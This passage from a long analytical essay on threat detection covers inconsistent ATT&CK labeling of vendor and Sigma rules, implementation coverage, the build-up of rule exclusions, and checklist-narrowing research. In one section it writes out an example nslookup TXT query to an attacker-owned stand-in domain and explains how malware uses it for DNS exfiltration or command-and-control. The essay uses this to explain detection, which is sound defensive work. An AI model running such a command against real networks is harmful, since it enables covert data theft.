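Products also labeled their own rules inconsistently. Carbon Black had two rules related to NotPetya, a destructive program that spread worldwide in 2017. Both applied to programs started by lsass.exe, the part of Windows that handles logins. One rule alerted on four known malicious programs, and the other alerted on any program that wasn't on a list of harmless ones. Any event that matched the narrow rule also matched the broad one, but only the broad rule was labeled OS Credential Dumping, the technique for stealing passwords.

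The number of labels per rule can distort coverage as well. About 84 percent of the commercial rules had one technique label, but one Splunk rule, which alerts when certain Windows programs start PowerShell, had six labels from five tactics. The six labels are defensible because the rule could fire at several stages of an attack. But they mean that one rule could add six techniques to a product's coverage, while a more cautious author would have added one or two.

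### One command with two apparent goals

The clearest example of the problem involves nslookup, a standard Windows tool for querying the Domain Name System (DNS). DNS translates names, such as a website's, into the numerical addresses computers use to find each other. A domain's owner can also attach short pieces of text to a name, and nslookup will fetch them if the user asks for that type of record.

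Attackers can use this to communicate, because many companies let DNS requests leave the network freely. Suppose malware runs the following command, and the attacker owns the domain:

`nslookup -q=txt k7f2a9.example.com`

The same command can be used to control malware or to send out stolen data. The text in the reply could contain an instruction for the malware, and the odd-looking first part of the name could be a fragment of stolen data, which reaches the attacker as part of the request.

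Elastic and Splunk both had a rule for this. Each rule alerts when someone runs nslookup with an option that selects the type of record, such as "-q=" or "-querytype=". Splunk's also alerts on the option "-retry=", which is the only difference that the researchers identified. The command above would set off both rules, but their labels differ:

| | Elastic | Splunk |
|---|---|---|
| Technique | Application Layer Protocol (T1071) | Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol (T1048) |
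| Tactic | Command and Control | Exfiltration |
| Apparent goal | To send instructions to a computer the attacker controls | To take data out of the network |

An analyst who trusted Elastic's label would probably look for the malware that sent the request and the commands it had received, while one who trusted Splunk's would want to know which files had left and whether the company had to notify anyone. Both would be sensible next steps, since the record contains the command but nothing about its purpose. However, neither analyst would know from the alert that the other's step was equally justified.

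The labels also affect the coverage figure. A company with Elastic's rule and no other rule for either technique would see Application Layer Protocol in green on its heatmap and Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol in red. If the company added Splunk's rule, the second cell would turn green too, though the company would gain the ability to detect the "-retry=" option and little else. If Elastic had chosen Splunk's label, adding Splunk's rule would not have raised the figure.

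### When varied labels do no harm

When the researchers shared their results with MITRE, one staff member replied that inconsistent labeling might not be a problem and could even be good. MITRE's staff think people should judge a product by what its rules detect rather than by its coverage. For someone who examines the rules, a label is a comment on the rule, and two vendors' comments can be more informative than one. For example, an analyst who saw both nslookup alerts would learn that the command has two plausible purposes.

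Virkud and colleagues largely accept this for experienced professionals who use ATT&CK to explain alerts. An experienced analyst would open the nslookup alert, see the command and consider both possibilities whatever the label. The pkexec labels are even less of a concern, since the reader would draw the same conclusion about the attacker's goal from each of them.

The argument fails once people or programs rely on the label without looking at the rule. A new analyst may take "Exfiltration" as a finding when it is only the rule author's guess, and software can make the same mistake. HOLMES and RapSheet, two research systems that piece attacks together from separate alerts, are built on the assumption that the underlying product will raise alerts for every tactic, which the study suggests rarely happens. Such a system could also place the same nslookup command at different stages of an attack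 depending on which vendor's rule fired.

Inconsistent labels do the most harm when someone adds them up to measure coverage. A buyer who compares two products' coverage percentages assumes that both vendors mean the same thing by each technique, but the vendors labeled most of the 37 threats differently. The difference between 48 and 55 percent is 13 techniques, and labeling choices could account for part of it, though nobody has measured how much.

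### Single rules and wrong labels in Sigma

Some labels are wrong, which is a separate problem from reasonable disagreement. The best recent evidence comes from Sigma, whose full history is public. Dhananjeyan and U used a snapshot that Long and Evans took on April 10, 2026, and examined the 2,355 rules whose detection logic had changed at least once. These rules covered 329 techniques, a count that must include sub-techniques because the catalog has only 227 techniques. It therefore can't be compared with the 151 that Sigma covered in 2022.

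The median technique had three rules, and one technique had 173. About a quarter of the techniques (84) had only one rule. The count leaves out rules whose logic never changed, so some of the 84 may have had a second rule in the collection. In the commercial products of 2022, roughly a fifth to a quarter of covered techniques also depended on a single rule.

A technique with only one rule loses all coverage if the company doesn't collect the records that the rule searches, or if an administrator turns the rule off because it is too noisy. The label must also be right. One Sigma rule detects failed attempts to access the database that Windows uses to manage its background services, but it is mislabeled as T1010, Application Window Discovery, which means finding out what windows are open on the screen.

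In January 2024, MITRE counted one Sigma rule for Application Window Discovery. If it was this mislabeled rule, which seems likely, a company that relied on Sigma would have seen the technique marked as covered even though none of its rules could detect it.

Sigma stores labels as plain text, and Dhananjeyan and U found that nothing enforces the format when someone writes a rule. One rule had the identifier of a data source where a tactic should have been. SigmaHQ's *Rule Validation* describes an optional check for such errors, which compares labels with MITRE's published data. It could flag an identifier that isn't in the catalog, but T1010 is a valid identifier and would pass, because no automatic check compares a label with what the rule detects.

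Labels can also make coverage look worse than it is. Of the 3,110 rules in Sigma's main collection, 348 were labeled with a tactic but no technique, so they didn't count toward technique coverage, whatever they could detect. Another 1,058 were labeled only with a broad technique when more specific sub-techniques existed. A company that measured coverage by sub-technique would not count those rules.

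Even a correct label may become wrong when a rule's detection logic changes. Long and Evans found that the logic had changed at least once in about 56 percent of the rules in both Sigma and Splunk's collection, and at least twice in half of those. An author who adds a condition to a rule may not think to review its label, but how often this happens is unknown. The overall error rate is also unknown, because Dhananjeyan and U's spot check found mistakes but did not measure how common they are.

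Some researchers propose using large language models to label rules. *Rule-ATT&CK Mapper (RAM)* (2025) describes manual labeling as slow and prone to errors, with about 670 techniques and sub-techniques to choose from. Version 20 of the catalog has 706. A model that processed every rule in the same way could make labels more consistent, and it might well catch errors such as a rule about background services being labeled as one about open windows.

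The nslookup rule alone is not enough to choose a label, because it contains no information about why someone ran the command. Virkud and colleagues suggest choosing the label when the alert fires, based on what else is happening on the computer. For instance, if someone had just gathered hundreds of documents into a compressed file, exfiltration would be the better guess.

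## What can go undetected when a technique counts as covered

A rule can be labeled with the right technique and still detect only a small part of it. For example, a rule that checks for the schtasks utility can miss an attacker who uses PowerShell instead. In September 2026, MITRE released a method for measuring such gaps.

A rule can also detect less over time, because maintainers add exclusions to stop false alarms and seldom remove them. In a study published in August 2026, Dhananjeyan and U tracked how exclusions build up in Sigma.

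### Counting implementations

MITRE's method adds a level, the implementation, between the technique and the procedure. Feffer defines an implementation as a behaviorally distinct way of carrying out a technique. Two attackers who run schtasks but choose different task names use the same implementation. An attacker who edits the Registry directly uses a different one, because the computer goes through different steps and leaves different records.

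Feffer's team built a catalog of implementations from ATT&CK's descriptions and procedure examples, along with tests from Atomic Red Team, a public library of small tests that imitate attacks. A large language model broke this material down into the steps and system interactions that each implementation requires. The team then linked those interactions to the telemetry fields that would record them. Its software, the Detection Coverage Calculator, reads rules in the Sigma format and works out which implementations they could observe:

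**implementation coverage = known implementations the rules can observe ÷ all known implementations**

Take a company that cares about four techniques and has at least one labeled rule for each:

| Technique | Known implementations | Implementations the rules observe | Implementation coverage |
|---|---|---|---|
| A | 8 | 2 | 25% |
| B | 5 | 1 | 20% |
| C | 4 | 1 | 25% |
| D | 3 | 3 | 100% |
| All four | 20 | 7 | 35% |

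The company's technique coverage is 100 percent, but its implementation coverage is 7/20, or 35 percent. It could write rules for the other 13 implementations without changing any cell in its heatmap. Averaging the four techniques' percentages would give 42.5 percent, because technique D would count as much as technique A. Anyone comparing two companies therefore needs to know which calculation each used.

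The probability of detecting an attack depends on how often attackers use each implementation, which neither figure takes into account. The company is much safer than 25 percent suggests if attackers nearly always use the two implementations of technique A that the rules observe, and less safe if they prefer the other six.

### Gaps in the implementation catalog

The denominator includes only listed implementations. Suppose technique A has four more. The company's true coverage is 7/24, or 29 percent, if its rules miss all four, and 11/24, or 46 percent, if they detect all four. A rule can detect implementations its author had never heard of if it is based on something every implementation of the technique must do. Still, the reported figure is probably too high more often than too low, since people write most rules with known implementations in mind.

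The catalog of implementations also has some of ATT&CK's gaps, because its procedure examples come from the same published reports as ATT&CK. The Atomic Red Team tests may fill some of these gaps, since a tester can write a test for a method before anyone has caught an attacker using it.

Someone also has to decide which implementations count as "behaviorally distinct". One analyst might treat every use of PowerShell to create a task as a single implementation, while another might split it into three. The company's score would change even though its rules had not, much as coverage changes with the labels that rule authors choose. A language model may group implementations more consistently than several analysts would, but it can also misread a report.

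### Robustness and precision

A rule that can detect an implementation is of little use if attackers can easily avoid it or if it constantly alerts on harmless activity. MITRE's method therefore also scores each rule's robustness and precision.

Robustness is the effort an attacker needs to evade a rule. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Summiting the Pyramid v3.0.0* (2025), an earlier version of the project, has five levels. Here they are with examples based on APT3's scheduled task:

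| Level | What the rule depends on | Example |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | A value the attacker can change at will | The task name "mysc" |
| 2 | A tool the attacker brought along | A trait of APT3's downloader |
| 3 | A tool already on the computer | The schtasks utility |
| 4 | Something that some implementations have in common | A record that several ways of creating a task produce |
| 5 | Something the technique can't do without | A record that every way of creating a task produces |

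Robustness also depends on where the record comes from. An attacker can avoid records made by an application more easily than those made by the kernel, the core of the operating system.

Precision is about false alarms. In the Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Definitions*, it is one of a pair of measures that often pull against each other:

**precision = malicious events the rule matches ÷ all events the rule matches**

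**recall = malicious events the rule matches ÷ all malicious events**

Imagine a company whose computers create 20,000 scheduled tasks a day, two of them malicious. A rule that alerts on every new task has perfect recall, but its precision is 2/20,000, or 0.01 percent. A rule that alerts only on tasks named "mysc" almost never raises a false alarm, but it misses any attacker who picks a different name.

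Better telemetry doesn't always show whether an action is malicious. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense, on its *detection engineering* page, uses the term "ambiguous technique" for a technique whose observable traces are not enough to determine intent. An administrator and an intruder can create a scheduled task in the same way, so an analyst has to look at the context to tell them apart.

The calculator takes its robustness and precision scores from a standard table of values for each type of record and field, which makes scoring fast and repeatable. But a rule's actual precision depends on how much similar, harmless activity a particular network has, and a standard value can't reflect that. New scheduled tasks, for example, might be rare on a hospital's scanners but constant on a software company's servers. The calculator's precision score is therefore best treated as a rough estimate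 of how noisy a rule will be.

MITRE's researchers also examined 144 Sigma rules that read Windows Security logs. *Putting Detection Coverage to the Test*, from the Center for Threat-Informed Defense, concludes that ATT&CK labels alone do not show the depth or quality of coverage. The 144 rules are less than 5 percent of Sigma's main collection, and other rules read different telemetry and may detect what these miss. The case study is therefore better evidence about ATT&CK labels than about how much Sigma as a whole can detect.

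### Why maintainers add exclusions

These scores describe a rule at one moment, but maintainers keep editing their rules, often because of false alarms. In the security operations center where only 0.01 percent of alerts were true attacks, another 49 percent correctly matched activity that had a business reason, according to Dhananjeyan and U, who cite a study by Yang and colleagues. For instance, a backup program may read a disk the same way as an attacker's tool.

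A maintainer whose detection rule keeps flagging harmless software has few good options. Removing the software is usually someone else's decision. A more precise rule takes time to write and test, and may be impossible if nothing in the logged data separates harmless activity from malicious activity. Lowering the rule's severity doesn't reduce the number of alerts, and deleting the rule loses everything it could detect. Adding an exclusion for the software is quick and leaves most of the rule intact.

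Excluding known activity can also make a rule practical to use. Suppose that known update programs create 19,900 of the 20,000 daily tasks in the example above. If the maintainer excludes them, the rule raises 100 alerts a day, which an analyst could realistically check, and its precision rises from 0.01 percent to 2 percent. But if one of the two malicious tasks also fits the exclusion, the rule misses half of the attacks.

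Sigma's maintainers made a decision of this kind in December 2022. One of their rules alerts when someone deletes or disables certain important scheduled tasks, including those of Windows Defender, Microsoft's antivirus software. Defender's upgrades remove and re-create its tasks, so every upgrade raised an alert. The maintainers added an exclusion for changes made by the computer's own account. Dhananjeyan and U consider the exclusion reasonable but note that nobody recorded when to reconsider it.

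### Why the label stays the same

A Sigma file has separate sections for ATT&CK labels and detection logic, so someone can add an exclusion to the logic without changing the labels. Because technique coverage depends only on whether a labeled rule exists, the exclusion cannot lower it, however broad.

Some exclusions are hard to notice even for people who look at the rule. In November 2021, a Sigma maintainer edited a rule that detects programs reading the memory of lsass.exe, the Windows login process. The maintainer added one program to the rule's existing list of harmless programs. That line was the only change to the file, and the "modified" date stayed the same.

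An exclusion removes part of what a rule detects, but the rule's technique label can't show a partial loss because it is either present or absent. Removing the label would usually be wrong, since the rule still detects the technique in most circumstances. Implementation coverage may not reveal the loss either, because a rule that excludes tasks created by one program can still detect the same implementation when any other program uses it.

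### Nine years of exclusions in Sigma

Dhananjeyan and U studied the 8,234 revisions that had changed the detection logic of a Sigma rule. They wrote a program to compare each version with the next. It counted the conditions that define what a rule looks for, the conditions that exclude something, and the separate values listed in those exclusions. It classed a revision as an added exclusion if it met this test:

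**added exclusion = (more exclusion conditions, or the same number with more values) and no increase in search conditions**

The last part is there because maintainers who extend a rule to a new kind of event often add an exclusion to limit the alerts the extension produces. Such a revision lets the rule detect more, so the researchers did not want to count it as narrowing.

| What happened in the revision | Number |
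|---|---|
| Exclusion added | 1,642 |
| Exclusion withdrawn | 304 |
| Search extended, with a new exclusion to limit it | 73 |
| Exclusions rewritten with no net change | 354 |
| No change to exclusions | 5,861 |

Maintainers added exclusions 5.4 times as often as they removed them. In 503 of the additions (31 percent), they only added a value to an existing list, as in the lsass.exe rule.

One of the researchers checked the program by labeling 120 revisions by hand. The researcher could judge 58 of those the program had classed as added exclusions, and 48 of them (83 percent) were correct. At that rate, about 1,359 of the 1,642 additions the program counted would be real, which is still 4.5 for each of the 304 withdrawals. Other errors make the ratio too low, such as when a maintainer replaces several specific exclusions with one broad one and the program counts a withdrawal. The exact ratio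 is uncertain, especially because only one person checked the program, but additions almost certainly far outnumber withdrawals.

The program counted additions or withdrawals of exclusions in only 559 of the study's 2,355 rules. Of those, 481 (86 percent) ended with more exclusions than they started with, and 37 ended with fewer. Growth in the number of rules doesn't explain the increase in exclusions, because the average number of net exclusions per active rule also rose, from less than 0.1 in the early years to about 0.57 in 2026.

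The maintainers' notes support alert overload as a cause. Words such as "false positive" or "noisy" appeared in the notes for 30.9 percent of the added exclusions that the researchers could match to a single edit, compared with 3.0 percent of revisions that neither added nor removed an exclusion. Most notes in Sigma are short, so the share of exclusions prompted by false alarms is probably higher.

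### How long exclusions last

Most of the exclusions were still in force when the data ended in April 2026, so nobody knows how long they will eventually last. Averaging only the finished ones would make exclusions look far more temporary than they are. The researchers used the Kaplan–Meier method, which medical researchers use to estimate survival when some patients are still alive at the end of a trial:

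**share surviving to time t = product, over every removal time up to t, of (1 − number removed ÷ number still being followed)**

For example, if maintainers remove 5 of 100 exclusions after a month, the estimated share still in place falls to 95 percent. Suppose the data then end for 15 others. These don't count as removals, but they leave only 80 exclusions to follow. If maintainers later remove 4 of those 80, 95 percent of them remain, so the estimate becomes 0.95 × 0.95, or about 90 percent.

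By this method, 96.6 percent of Sigma's exclusions were still in place after one month, 89.9 percent after one year and 86.7 percent after three years. The estimate covers 1,584 exclusions, of which maintainers removed 203. It leaves out 58 with no measurable duration, mostly to avoid counting corrections made during a single edit. It may slightly understate how long exclusions last, because the program could match a removal to the wrong exclusion in the same rule.

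A long-lived exclusion may be as useful as when it was added if the harmless software is still in use. However, 76 percent of the removals happened within a year, and almost none happened after two years, which suggests that maintainers rarely go back to old exclusions. Dhananjeyan and U propose that this is because people usually review a rule when it has raised an alert, and an exclusion prevents the alerts that would lead someone to question it. This explanation fits the timing, but they did not test it.

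One rule in the study alerts when a program loads a Windows component for managing backup snapshots. Backup software does this routinely, and ransomware does it just before encrypting files. Maintainers added 27 exclusions to the rule. In April 2026, 24 were still there, and the other three had changed only in spelling. One exclusion covers all of Program Files, the main folder for installed software. In a comment, the maintainer asks users to replace it with the exact applications they have. The broad exclusion had been in the public version for three and a half years.

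Exclusions in a rule that is the only one for its technique stayed in force about as often as exclusions in other rules, even though no other rule is there to catch what they let through. Dhananjeyan and U found 71 exclusions in such rules, of which 63 (89 percent) were still in force, compared with 1,093 of 1,268 (86 percent) in rules whose techniques had other rules too. A log-rank test, which compares two survival curves over their whole length, gave a p-value of 0.49, so a difference at least this large would arise by chance about half the time if the two groups did not really differ.

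The researchers conclude that whether an exclusion persists does not depend on whether its technique has other rules. The data show no sign of a dependence, but they can't rule it out. Maintainers removed only eight exclusions from the single-rule group, so the test could easily miss a moderate difference. The grouping also relies on labels as they stood in April 2026, and a rule that is now the only one for its technique may have been one of several when the maintainer added the exclusion.

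### What an exclusion costs the defender

Some exclusions give attackers almost nothing. If a rule excludes a program in a protected system folder, an intruder usually needs administrator rights to exploit it. Dhananjeyan and U classified 5,336 file locations and names that appeared in exclusions. For 33 percent, an attacker would first need the right to write to a protected folder, but an ordinary program without special rights could match the exclusion for 64 percent.

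The study did not look for attacks that used an exclusion. Dhananjeyan and U cite an experiment in which Uetz and colleagues evaded nearly half of the widely used rules they tested in a real company network. That experiment was about weaknesses in rules generally, so it doesn't show how many attacks succeed because of exclusions.

The classification helps maintainers decide where to start. The researchers suggest first reviewing the roughly 12 percent of values that were both broad and open to any program, and leaving alone another 18 percent that named one specific file in a protected folder. Maintainers can't determine from either test whether the excluded software is harmless, because that depends on the network.

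An exclusion in Sigma also affects people who had no part in the decision to add it. Sigma's maintainers list AlphaSOC and AttackIQ among the companies whose products use or integrate its rules. A company that copies the public rules also copies exclusions for software it may never have installed. It can remove these exclusions from its copy, but only if it notices them. Companies can also add their own exclusions, but they keep these private, so nobody can tell whether the pattern in Sigma is typical of the rules companies run.

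### Whether rules narrow overall

Dhananjeyan and U conclude that "Detection rules narrow over time", but their evidence firmly supports only the more limited claim that exclusions accumulate. Maintainers can add exclusions to a rule while also extending what it detects, and the earlier study by Long and Evans suggests that they often do.

Long and Evans had GPT-5, an OpenAI model, compare successive versions of each rule and infer why the maintainers had changed it:

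| Inferred purpose of the revision | Sigma | Splunk |
|---|---|---|
| Detect more | 41.3% | 35.9% |
| Reduce false alarms | 30.2% | 18.0% |
| Both | 12.0% | 11.4% |
| Unclear | 16.5% | 34.6% |

In both collections, more revisions seem to have broadened a rule than narrowed it. The model's answers mostly agreed with a separate analysis of the rules' structure, but Long and Evans did not ask the maintainers why they made the changes. The counts also ignore the size of each change, so a revision that adds a rare attack tool to a rule counts the same as one that excludes an entire folder. Without testing old and new versions on the same records, nobody can say whether the typical rule now detects more attacks or fewer.

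The timing suggests that maintainers face more immediate pressure to reduce false alarms than to detect more. The median gap between two consecutive classified revisions of a Sigma rule was 32 days when both aimed to reduce false alarms and 125 days when both aimed to detect more. Long and Evans think this is because a false alarm shows up soon after people start using a rule and needs a quick fix, while maintainers add coverage more slowly as new threats emerge.

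About 30 percent of the revised Sigma rules and 26 percent of the revised Splunk rules had some revisions meant to detect more and others meant to reduce false alarms. Sometimes one kind of change required the other. For example, one Sigma rule detects well-known system tools that someone has renamed, a common way to disguise them. Each time the maintainers added a tool to the rule, they also had to exclude that tool under its normal name, or the rule would have alerted on every legitimate use.

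In other cases the maintainers seem not to have settled on what the rule should do. A Splunk rule for new local administrator accounts looks for two Windows events: the creation of an account and its addition to the administrators' group. One version can raise an alert on only one of the events, while another requires both. The maintainers switched to the stricter version, changed back in the next revision, and tried combining the two versions about 13 months later. An attacker who triggered only one of the events could have set off an alert under one version but not the next, though the rule would have counted the same toward technique coverage under both.

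## Whether a list of categories narrows what people look for

Detection rules are plentiful for some techniques and missing for others, and commercial products tend to have the same gaps. ATT&CK may have contributed to this pattern by drawing attention to the behaviors it lists, but vendors might have written much the same rules without it. The difference matters to taxonomy designers because a better list will help only if it affects what people look for.

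### Other explanations for the pattern

The simplest alternative explanation is that defenders write rules for whatever their software records. Each Sigma rule specifies a log source, which limits what the rule can detect, as Dhananjeyan and U point out. Endpoint products can't observe many of the 53 techniques that lack a commercial rule, and those gaps would probably exist with any catalog or none. But missing data can't explain every gap, because CardinalOps's customers already collected enough data to cover far more techniques than they did.

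Vendors may also make similar choices because they read the same threat reports. If so, one might expect their rules to mention the same threats, but most of the named threats that Virkud and colleagues found appeared in only one product's rules. This is weak evidence against the explanation, because the researchers think every vendor had probably examined reports on all of these threats, and some may have decided that their general rules were enough.

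Copying would be easy because Elastic, Splunk and Sigma publish their rules. The small overlap in named threats is slight evidence against copying, since a copied rule would often keep the threat's name in its description. Comparing the rules' dates would be a better test, because if vendors copy, new rules in one collection should often follow similar rules in another.

Finally, vendors may write the most rules for the techniques that attackers use most, which would be sensible. Some techniques may have no rules because attackers rarely use them. Virkud and colleagues suggest this for two techniques whose lack of rules had no other obvious explanation, but they could not confirm it. Comparing rule counts with sightings would not settle the matter, because defenders are more likely to see techniques they already have rules for.

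These causes can also work together with the catalog. A report might lead MITRE to list a technique, and the listing might then prompt a vendor that missed the report to write a rule.

ATT&CK listed all 53 techniques that had no commercial rule, so listing a behavior is not enough to get a rule written. But narrowing would mostly affect behaviors that ATT&CK does not list, and a study that sorts rules by ATT&CK technique can't measure those. The unlabeled rules that Virkud and colleagues set aside were mainly simple blocklists of network addresses, so either vendors write few rules for unlisted behaviors, or rule authors label such rules with the nearest technique.

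### Tests that nobody seems to have run

No published experiment appears to compare security analysts working with and without ATT&CK. In *SoK*, a 2023 review of research on the catalog, Roy, Panaousis and colleagues called for more work on how it performs in practice. A later review, *MITRE ATT&CK Applications in Cybersecurity and The Way Forward* (2025), found that most evaluations test tools and algorithms on datasets or simulated attacks, and fewer ask experts for their opinions. Researchers have run experiments with other security catalogs, but at least some of these experiments measured the overall quality of people's answers rather than the number of threats they missed.

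Researchers could test this directly with a fairly simple experiment. They would give two groups of analysts the records of the same staged intrusion, including some behaviors that ATT&CK lists and some that it doesn't, but give only one group the catalog. If that group found more of the listed behaviors and fewer of the unlisted ones than the other group, the catalog would have narrowed its search.

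The revision history of public rules could provide another test, using work that people have already done. Long and Evans assembled 6,859 rule histories, which begin in December 2016 for Sigma and December 2018 for Splunk, and published the software they used to analyze them. A researcher could choose a behavior that MITRE added during those years and count the new rules for it before and after the release. The researcher would have to identify these rules by their detection logic, because no rule could carry the technique's label before the technique existed. The same count for similar behaviors whose status in the catalog did not change would give a comparison:

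**estimated effect of listing = change in new rules for the listed behavior − change in new rules for comparison behaviors**

Suppose maintainers wrote two rules a year for a behavior before MITRE listed it and six a year afterwards, while the comparison behaviors went from two to four. The estimated effect of listing would be two extra rules a year. Without the comparison, the estimate would be four, because it would include general growth in rule writing. This is a risk with Sigma, whose contributors wrote rules at an increasing rate from 2019 through 2022. Choosing comparison behaviors that appear in the same kind of record would also help keep differences in telemetry from distorting the result.

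A harder problem is that one report of an attack can lead both MITRE to list a behavior and vendors to write rules for it. MITRE's release schedule can help separate the report's effect on vendors from the catalog's, because reports come out all year but major releases come out only twice a year. If new rules cluster soon after the reports, the reports are the more likely cause, but if they cluster after the release, even for behaviors reported many months earlier, the catalog probably had its own effect.

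To test for narrowing, the researcher would also need to check whether rules for unlisted behaviors became rarer when MITRE added new techniques. Even then, the histories could not show how people wrote rules before ATT&CK, because ATT&CK was public more than a year before Sigma's first rule.

In the existing data, Sigma's maintainers kept exclusions about as often in a technique's only rule as in other rules. If they were managing the collection by technique, they would probably be more careful with the only rule. This is a small clue, but it suggests that the catalog may have little influence on how people maintain rules, even if it influences which rules they write.

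### Searching for one thing and missing another

The closest evidence comes from other fields. In *The Invisible Gorilla Strikes Again* (2013), Drew, Võ and Wolfe asked 24 radiologists to search chest CT scans for lung nodules, small spots that can be cancerous. The researchers had inserted a picture of a gorilla, 48 times the size of the average nodule, into the last scan. Twenty of the radiologists did not report seeing it, although eye tracking showed that most of those 20 had looked directly at it.

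Radiologists have no reason to look for a gorilla, so the researchers' next experiment used abnormalities that matter to patients. According to the University of Utah, 50 radiologists checked seven chest scans for lung cancer, and the last scan also contained a large breast mass and an abnormal lymph node. Two-thirds missed the mass and a third missed the lymph node. Williams, Drew and colleagues then asked another 30 radiologists to look for a broader range of abnormalities (*The Invisible Breast Cancer*, 2021). Only 3 percent missed the mass and 10 percent missed the lymph node. This is the best evidence that the instruction to look for lung cancer caused the misses, since most radiologists saw both abnormalities when asked to search more broadly.

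People may also stop searching once they have found something, as when a doctor finds a serious head injury and doesn't check for a neck injury. Radiologists call this "satisfaction of search", but the evidence for it is mixed. *Satisfaction of Search in Chest Radiography 2015*, by Berbaum and colleagues, tested 20 radiologists on chest images with and without an added nodule. The nodule made them more reluctant to report other abnormalities, but it did not shorten their search or make them worse at telling normal images from abnormal ones. The equivalent in security would be an analyst who finds one clear sign of an intruder and then dismisses a second, fainter one.

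### How accident manuals shape the causes people find

Writing detection rules is slower and more deliberate than reading a scan, and in that respect more like investigating an accident. Lundberg, Rollenhagen and Hollnagel studied eight manuals for accident investigators in *What-You-Look-For-Is-What-You-Find* (2009). Every manual contains some model of how accidents happen, even if it doesn't state one. All eight used what the researchers call complex linear models, in which an accident results from a chain of events combined with underlying weaknesses. The manuals generally directed investigators to the same kinds of factors: people, technology, organization and information.

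The researchers argue that the causes investigators find reflect the model they started with, and that organizations then typically try to fix those causes. If a manual omits a kind of cause, an organization could investigate many accidents carefully and never address it. A security team that plans its work from a heatmap could likewise fail to address unlisted behaviors.

This evidence is weaker than that from the radiology experiments because the researchers compared manuals rather than giving the same accident to investigators with different manuals. Investigators with similar manuals may also reach similar findings because the accidents themselves have similar causes, just as vendors may write similar rules because they face similar attacks.

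### Checklists that leave out the right answer

There is also good evidence that lists help. AHRQ, the US government's agency for research on healthcare quality, cites several studies in which a checklist reduced errors in reading electrocardiograms, which trace the heart's electrical activity. Other checklists with specific medical content have also helped, though often only slightly or only for some clinicians. Results like these don't show whether a list also makes people miss what it leaves out. To find out, researchers also have to measure how well people notice unlisted items.

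Kämmer, Schauber and colleagues (2021), in *Differential diagnosis checklists reduce diagnostic error differentially*, tested a diagnostic checklist with 90 medical students in Berlin. Each student diagnosed six simulated patients who were short of breath, choosing from 30 diagnostic tests. Some students received a list of 17 possible diagnoses, which included the correct one for three of the six patients. The researchers warned these students that the list might not contain the right answer.

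*Primers or Reminders?* (Spadini, Çalikli and Bacchelli, 2020) reports a similar test with 85 software developers. Each developer reviewed a piece of code for bugs, and about half could see an earlier reviewer's comment pointing out one bug. Some saw a comment about a missing value that could crash the program, a type of bug reviewers seldom check for, and others saw one about an error in an unusual case, a type they commonly look for. The code also contained one more bug of each type.

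| Experiment | What people had to find | Without the list or comment | With it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kämmer and colleagues | A diagnosis on the list | 49% | 75% |
| Kämmer and colleagues | A diagnosis not on the list | 49% | 43% |
| Spadini and colleagues, missing-value comment | Another bug of the same type | 12% | 62% |
| Spadini and colleagues, missing-value comment | A bug of the other type | 82% | 67% |
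| Spadini and colleagues, unusual-case comment | Another bug of the same type | 32% | 45% |
| Spadini and colleagues, unusual-case comment | A bug of the other type | 64% | 59% |

The large gains, for listed diagnoses and for bugs with missing values, are very unlikely to be due to chance. Results for unlisted items were lower in all three comparisons, but none of the drops was statistically significant, and chance alone would produce three drops out of three one time in eight. Spadini and colleagues conclude that comments act as useful reminders and do not distract reviewers from other bugs. They may be right, but only 38 developers took part in the comparison with the 15-point drop, so it could easily have missed a real loss. They also found no sign that developers who had found one bug were less likely to find a second.

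The students' notes are more direct evidence against narrowing. Students whose list lacked the correct diagnosis still wrote it down as a possibility in 66 percent of cases, compared with 69 percent for students who had to write down their ideas without a list. An incomplete list seems to have had little effect on whether students thought of the correct diagnosis.

Even if the drop for unlisted diagnoses were real, the list could still be worth using:

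**net change in accuracy = share of cases on the list × gain − share not on the list × loss**

If a list raises accuracy by 26 points when it contains the right answer and lowers it by 6 when it doesn't, it would do more good than harm as long as it contained the right answer in more than about 19 percent of cases. The students with lists also had to write down their ideas, so it may be fairer to compare them with the students who did so without a list, who got 53 percent of diagnoses right. On that comparison, the list would have to contain the right answer in more than about 31 percent of cases. A reasonably complete list would easily exceed either threshold.

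Students whose list lacked the right answer were more confident than students without a list, but no more accurate. On a scale from 10 to 100, they rated their confidence at 68 on average, compared with 59 for students without a list. They also spent about 80 seconds longer on each patient, which may have made them feel more thorough.

### Applying these results to security teams

A radiologist may spend only minutes on a scan, while a security team can work on its rules for weeks. Its members can search the same logs again, use different tools and check each other's work. A momentary lapse of attention should therefore matter less when a team writes rules than when an analyst works through a long queue of alerts. But the extra time helps only if someone thinks to look for the missing behavior, and no alert will prompt them to look if there is no rule for it.

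ATT&CK is also far broader than an instruction to look for lung nodules. The students who worked without a list wrote down fewer than four diagnoses per patient, and a security analyst working from memory would surely list fewer than 227 techniques. For most analysts, especially new ones, the catalog probably widens the search overall, even if it draws some attention away from unlisted behaviors.

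The break-even calculation is less reassuring in security because it assumes a fixed share of unlisted cases. Attackers, unlike diseases, can read ATT&CK and the public rules and choose methods that appear in neither. A small loss on unlisted behaviors could then do more harm over time. The students' extra confidence is also a concern, because a team that feels well covered may spend less time looking for unlisted behaviors.

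When people consult a catalog might matter too. Some experienced risk analysts prefer to brainstorm threats first and then check the catalog for anything they missed. That should keep most of the list's benefit without narrowing the first search. Researchers could test this by adding a third group to the experiment with two groups of analysts and giving it the catalog only after a first search.

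## How coverage became a sales claim and a compliance target

An ATT&CK label starts as a note from a rule's author to the analyst who will read the alert. Once people count the labels, the total can end up in an advertisement, a purchasing decision, a yearly goal or an audit. Many of the people who use the total in these ways have never read the rules, and some have reasons to want a higher number.

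Goodhart's law describes the risk. Charles Goodhart, a British economist, observed in 1975 that statistical patterns tend to break down once governments use them to control the economy. People now apply the law much more widely, to mean that a measure stops measuring well when someone turns it into a target. A count of labeled rules might be a fair guide to a product's strength as long as nothing depends on it. If sales depend on it, the vendor has a reason to raise the count, and some ways of doing so are much cheaper than improving detection:

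| Who uses the number | What they use it for | How it could rise, or stay high, without better detection |
|---|---|---|
| Rule author | Explaining an alert | Putting several labels on one rule |
| Vendor | Winning customers | Writing weak rules for techniques that have none, or advertising the most flattering count |
| Buyer | Choosing a product | Adding a second product that detects the same behavior under different labels |
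| Security chief | Showing progress | Writing the easiest missing rules first |
| Auditor or insurer | Judging risk | Clients keeping broken or noisy rules because removing them would lower the figure |

All of these are possible, but the evidence that they happen is much better for vendors than for auditors or insurers.

### Advertisements and buyers

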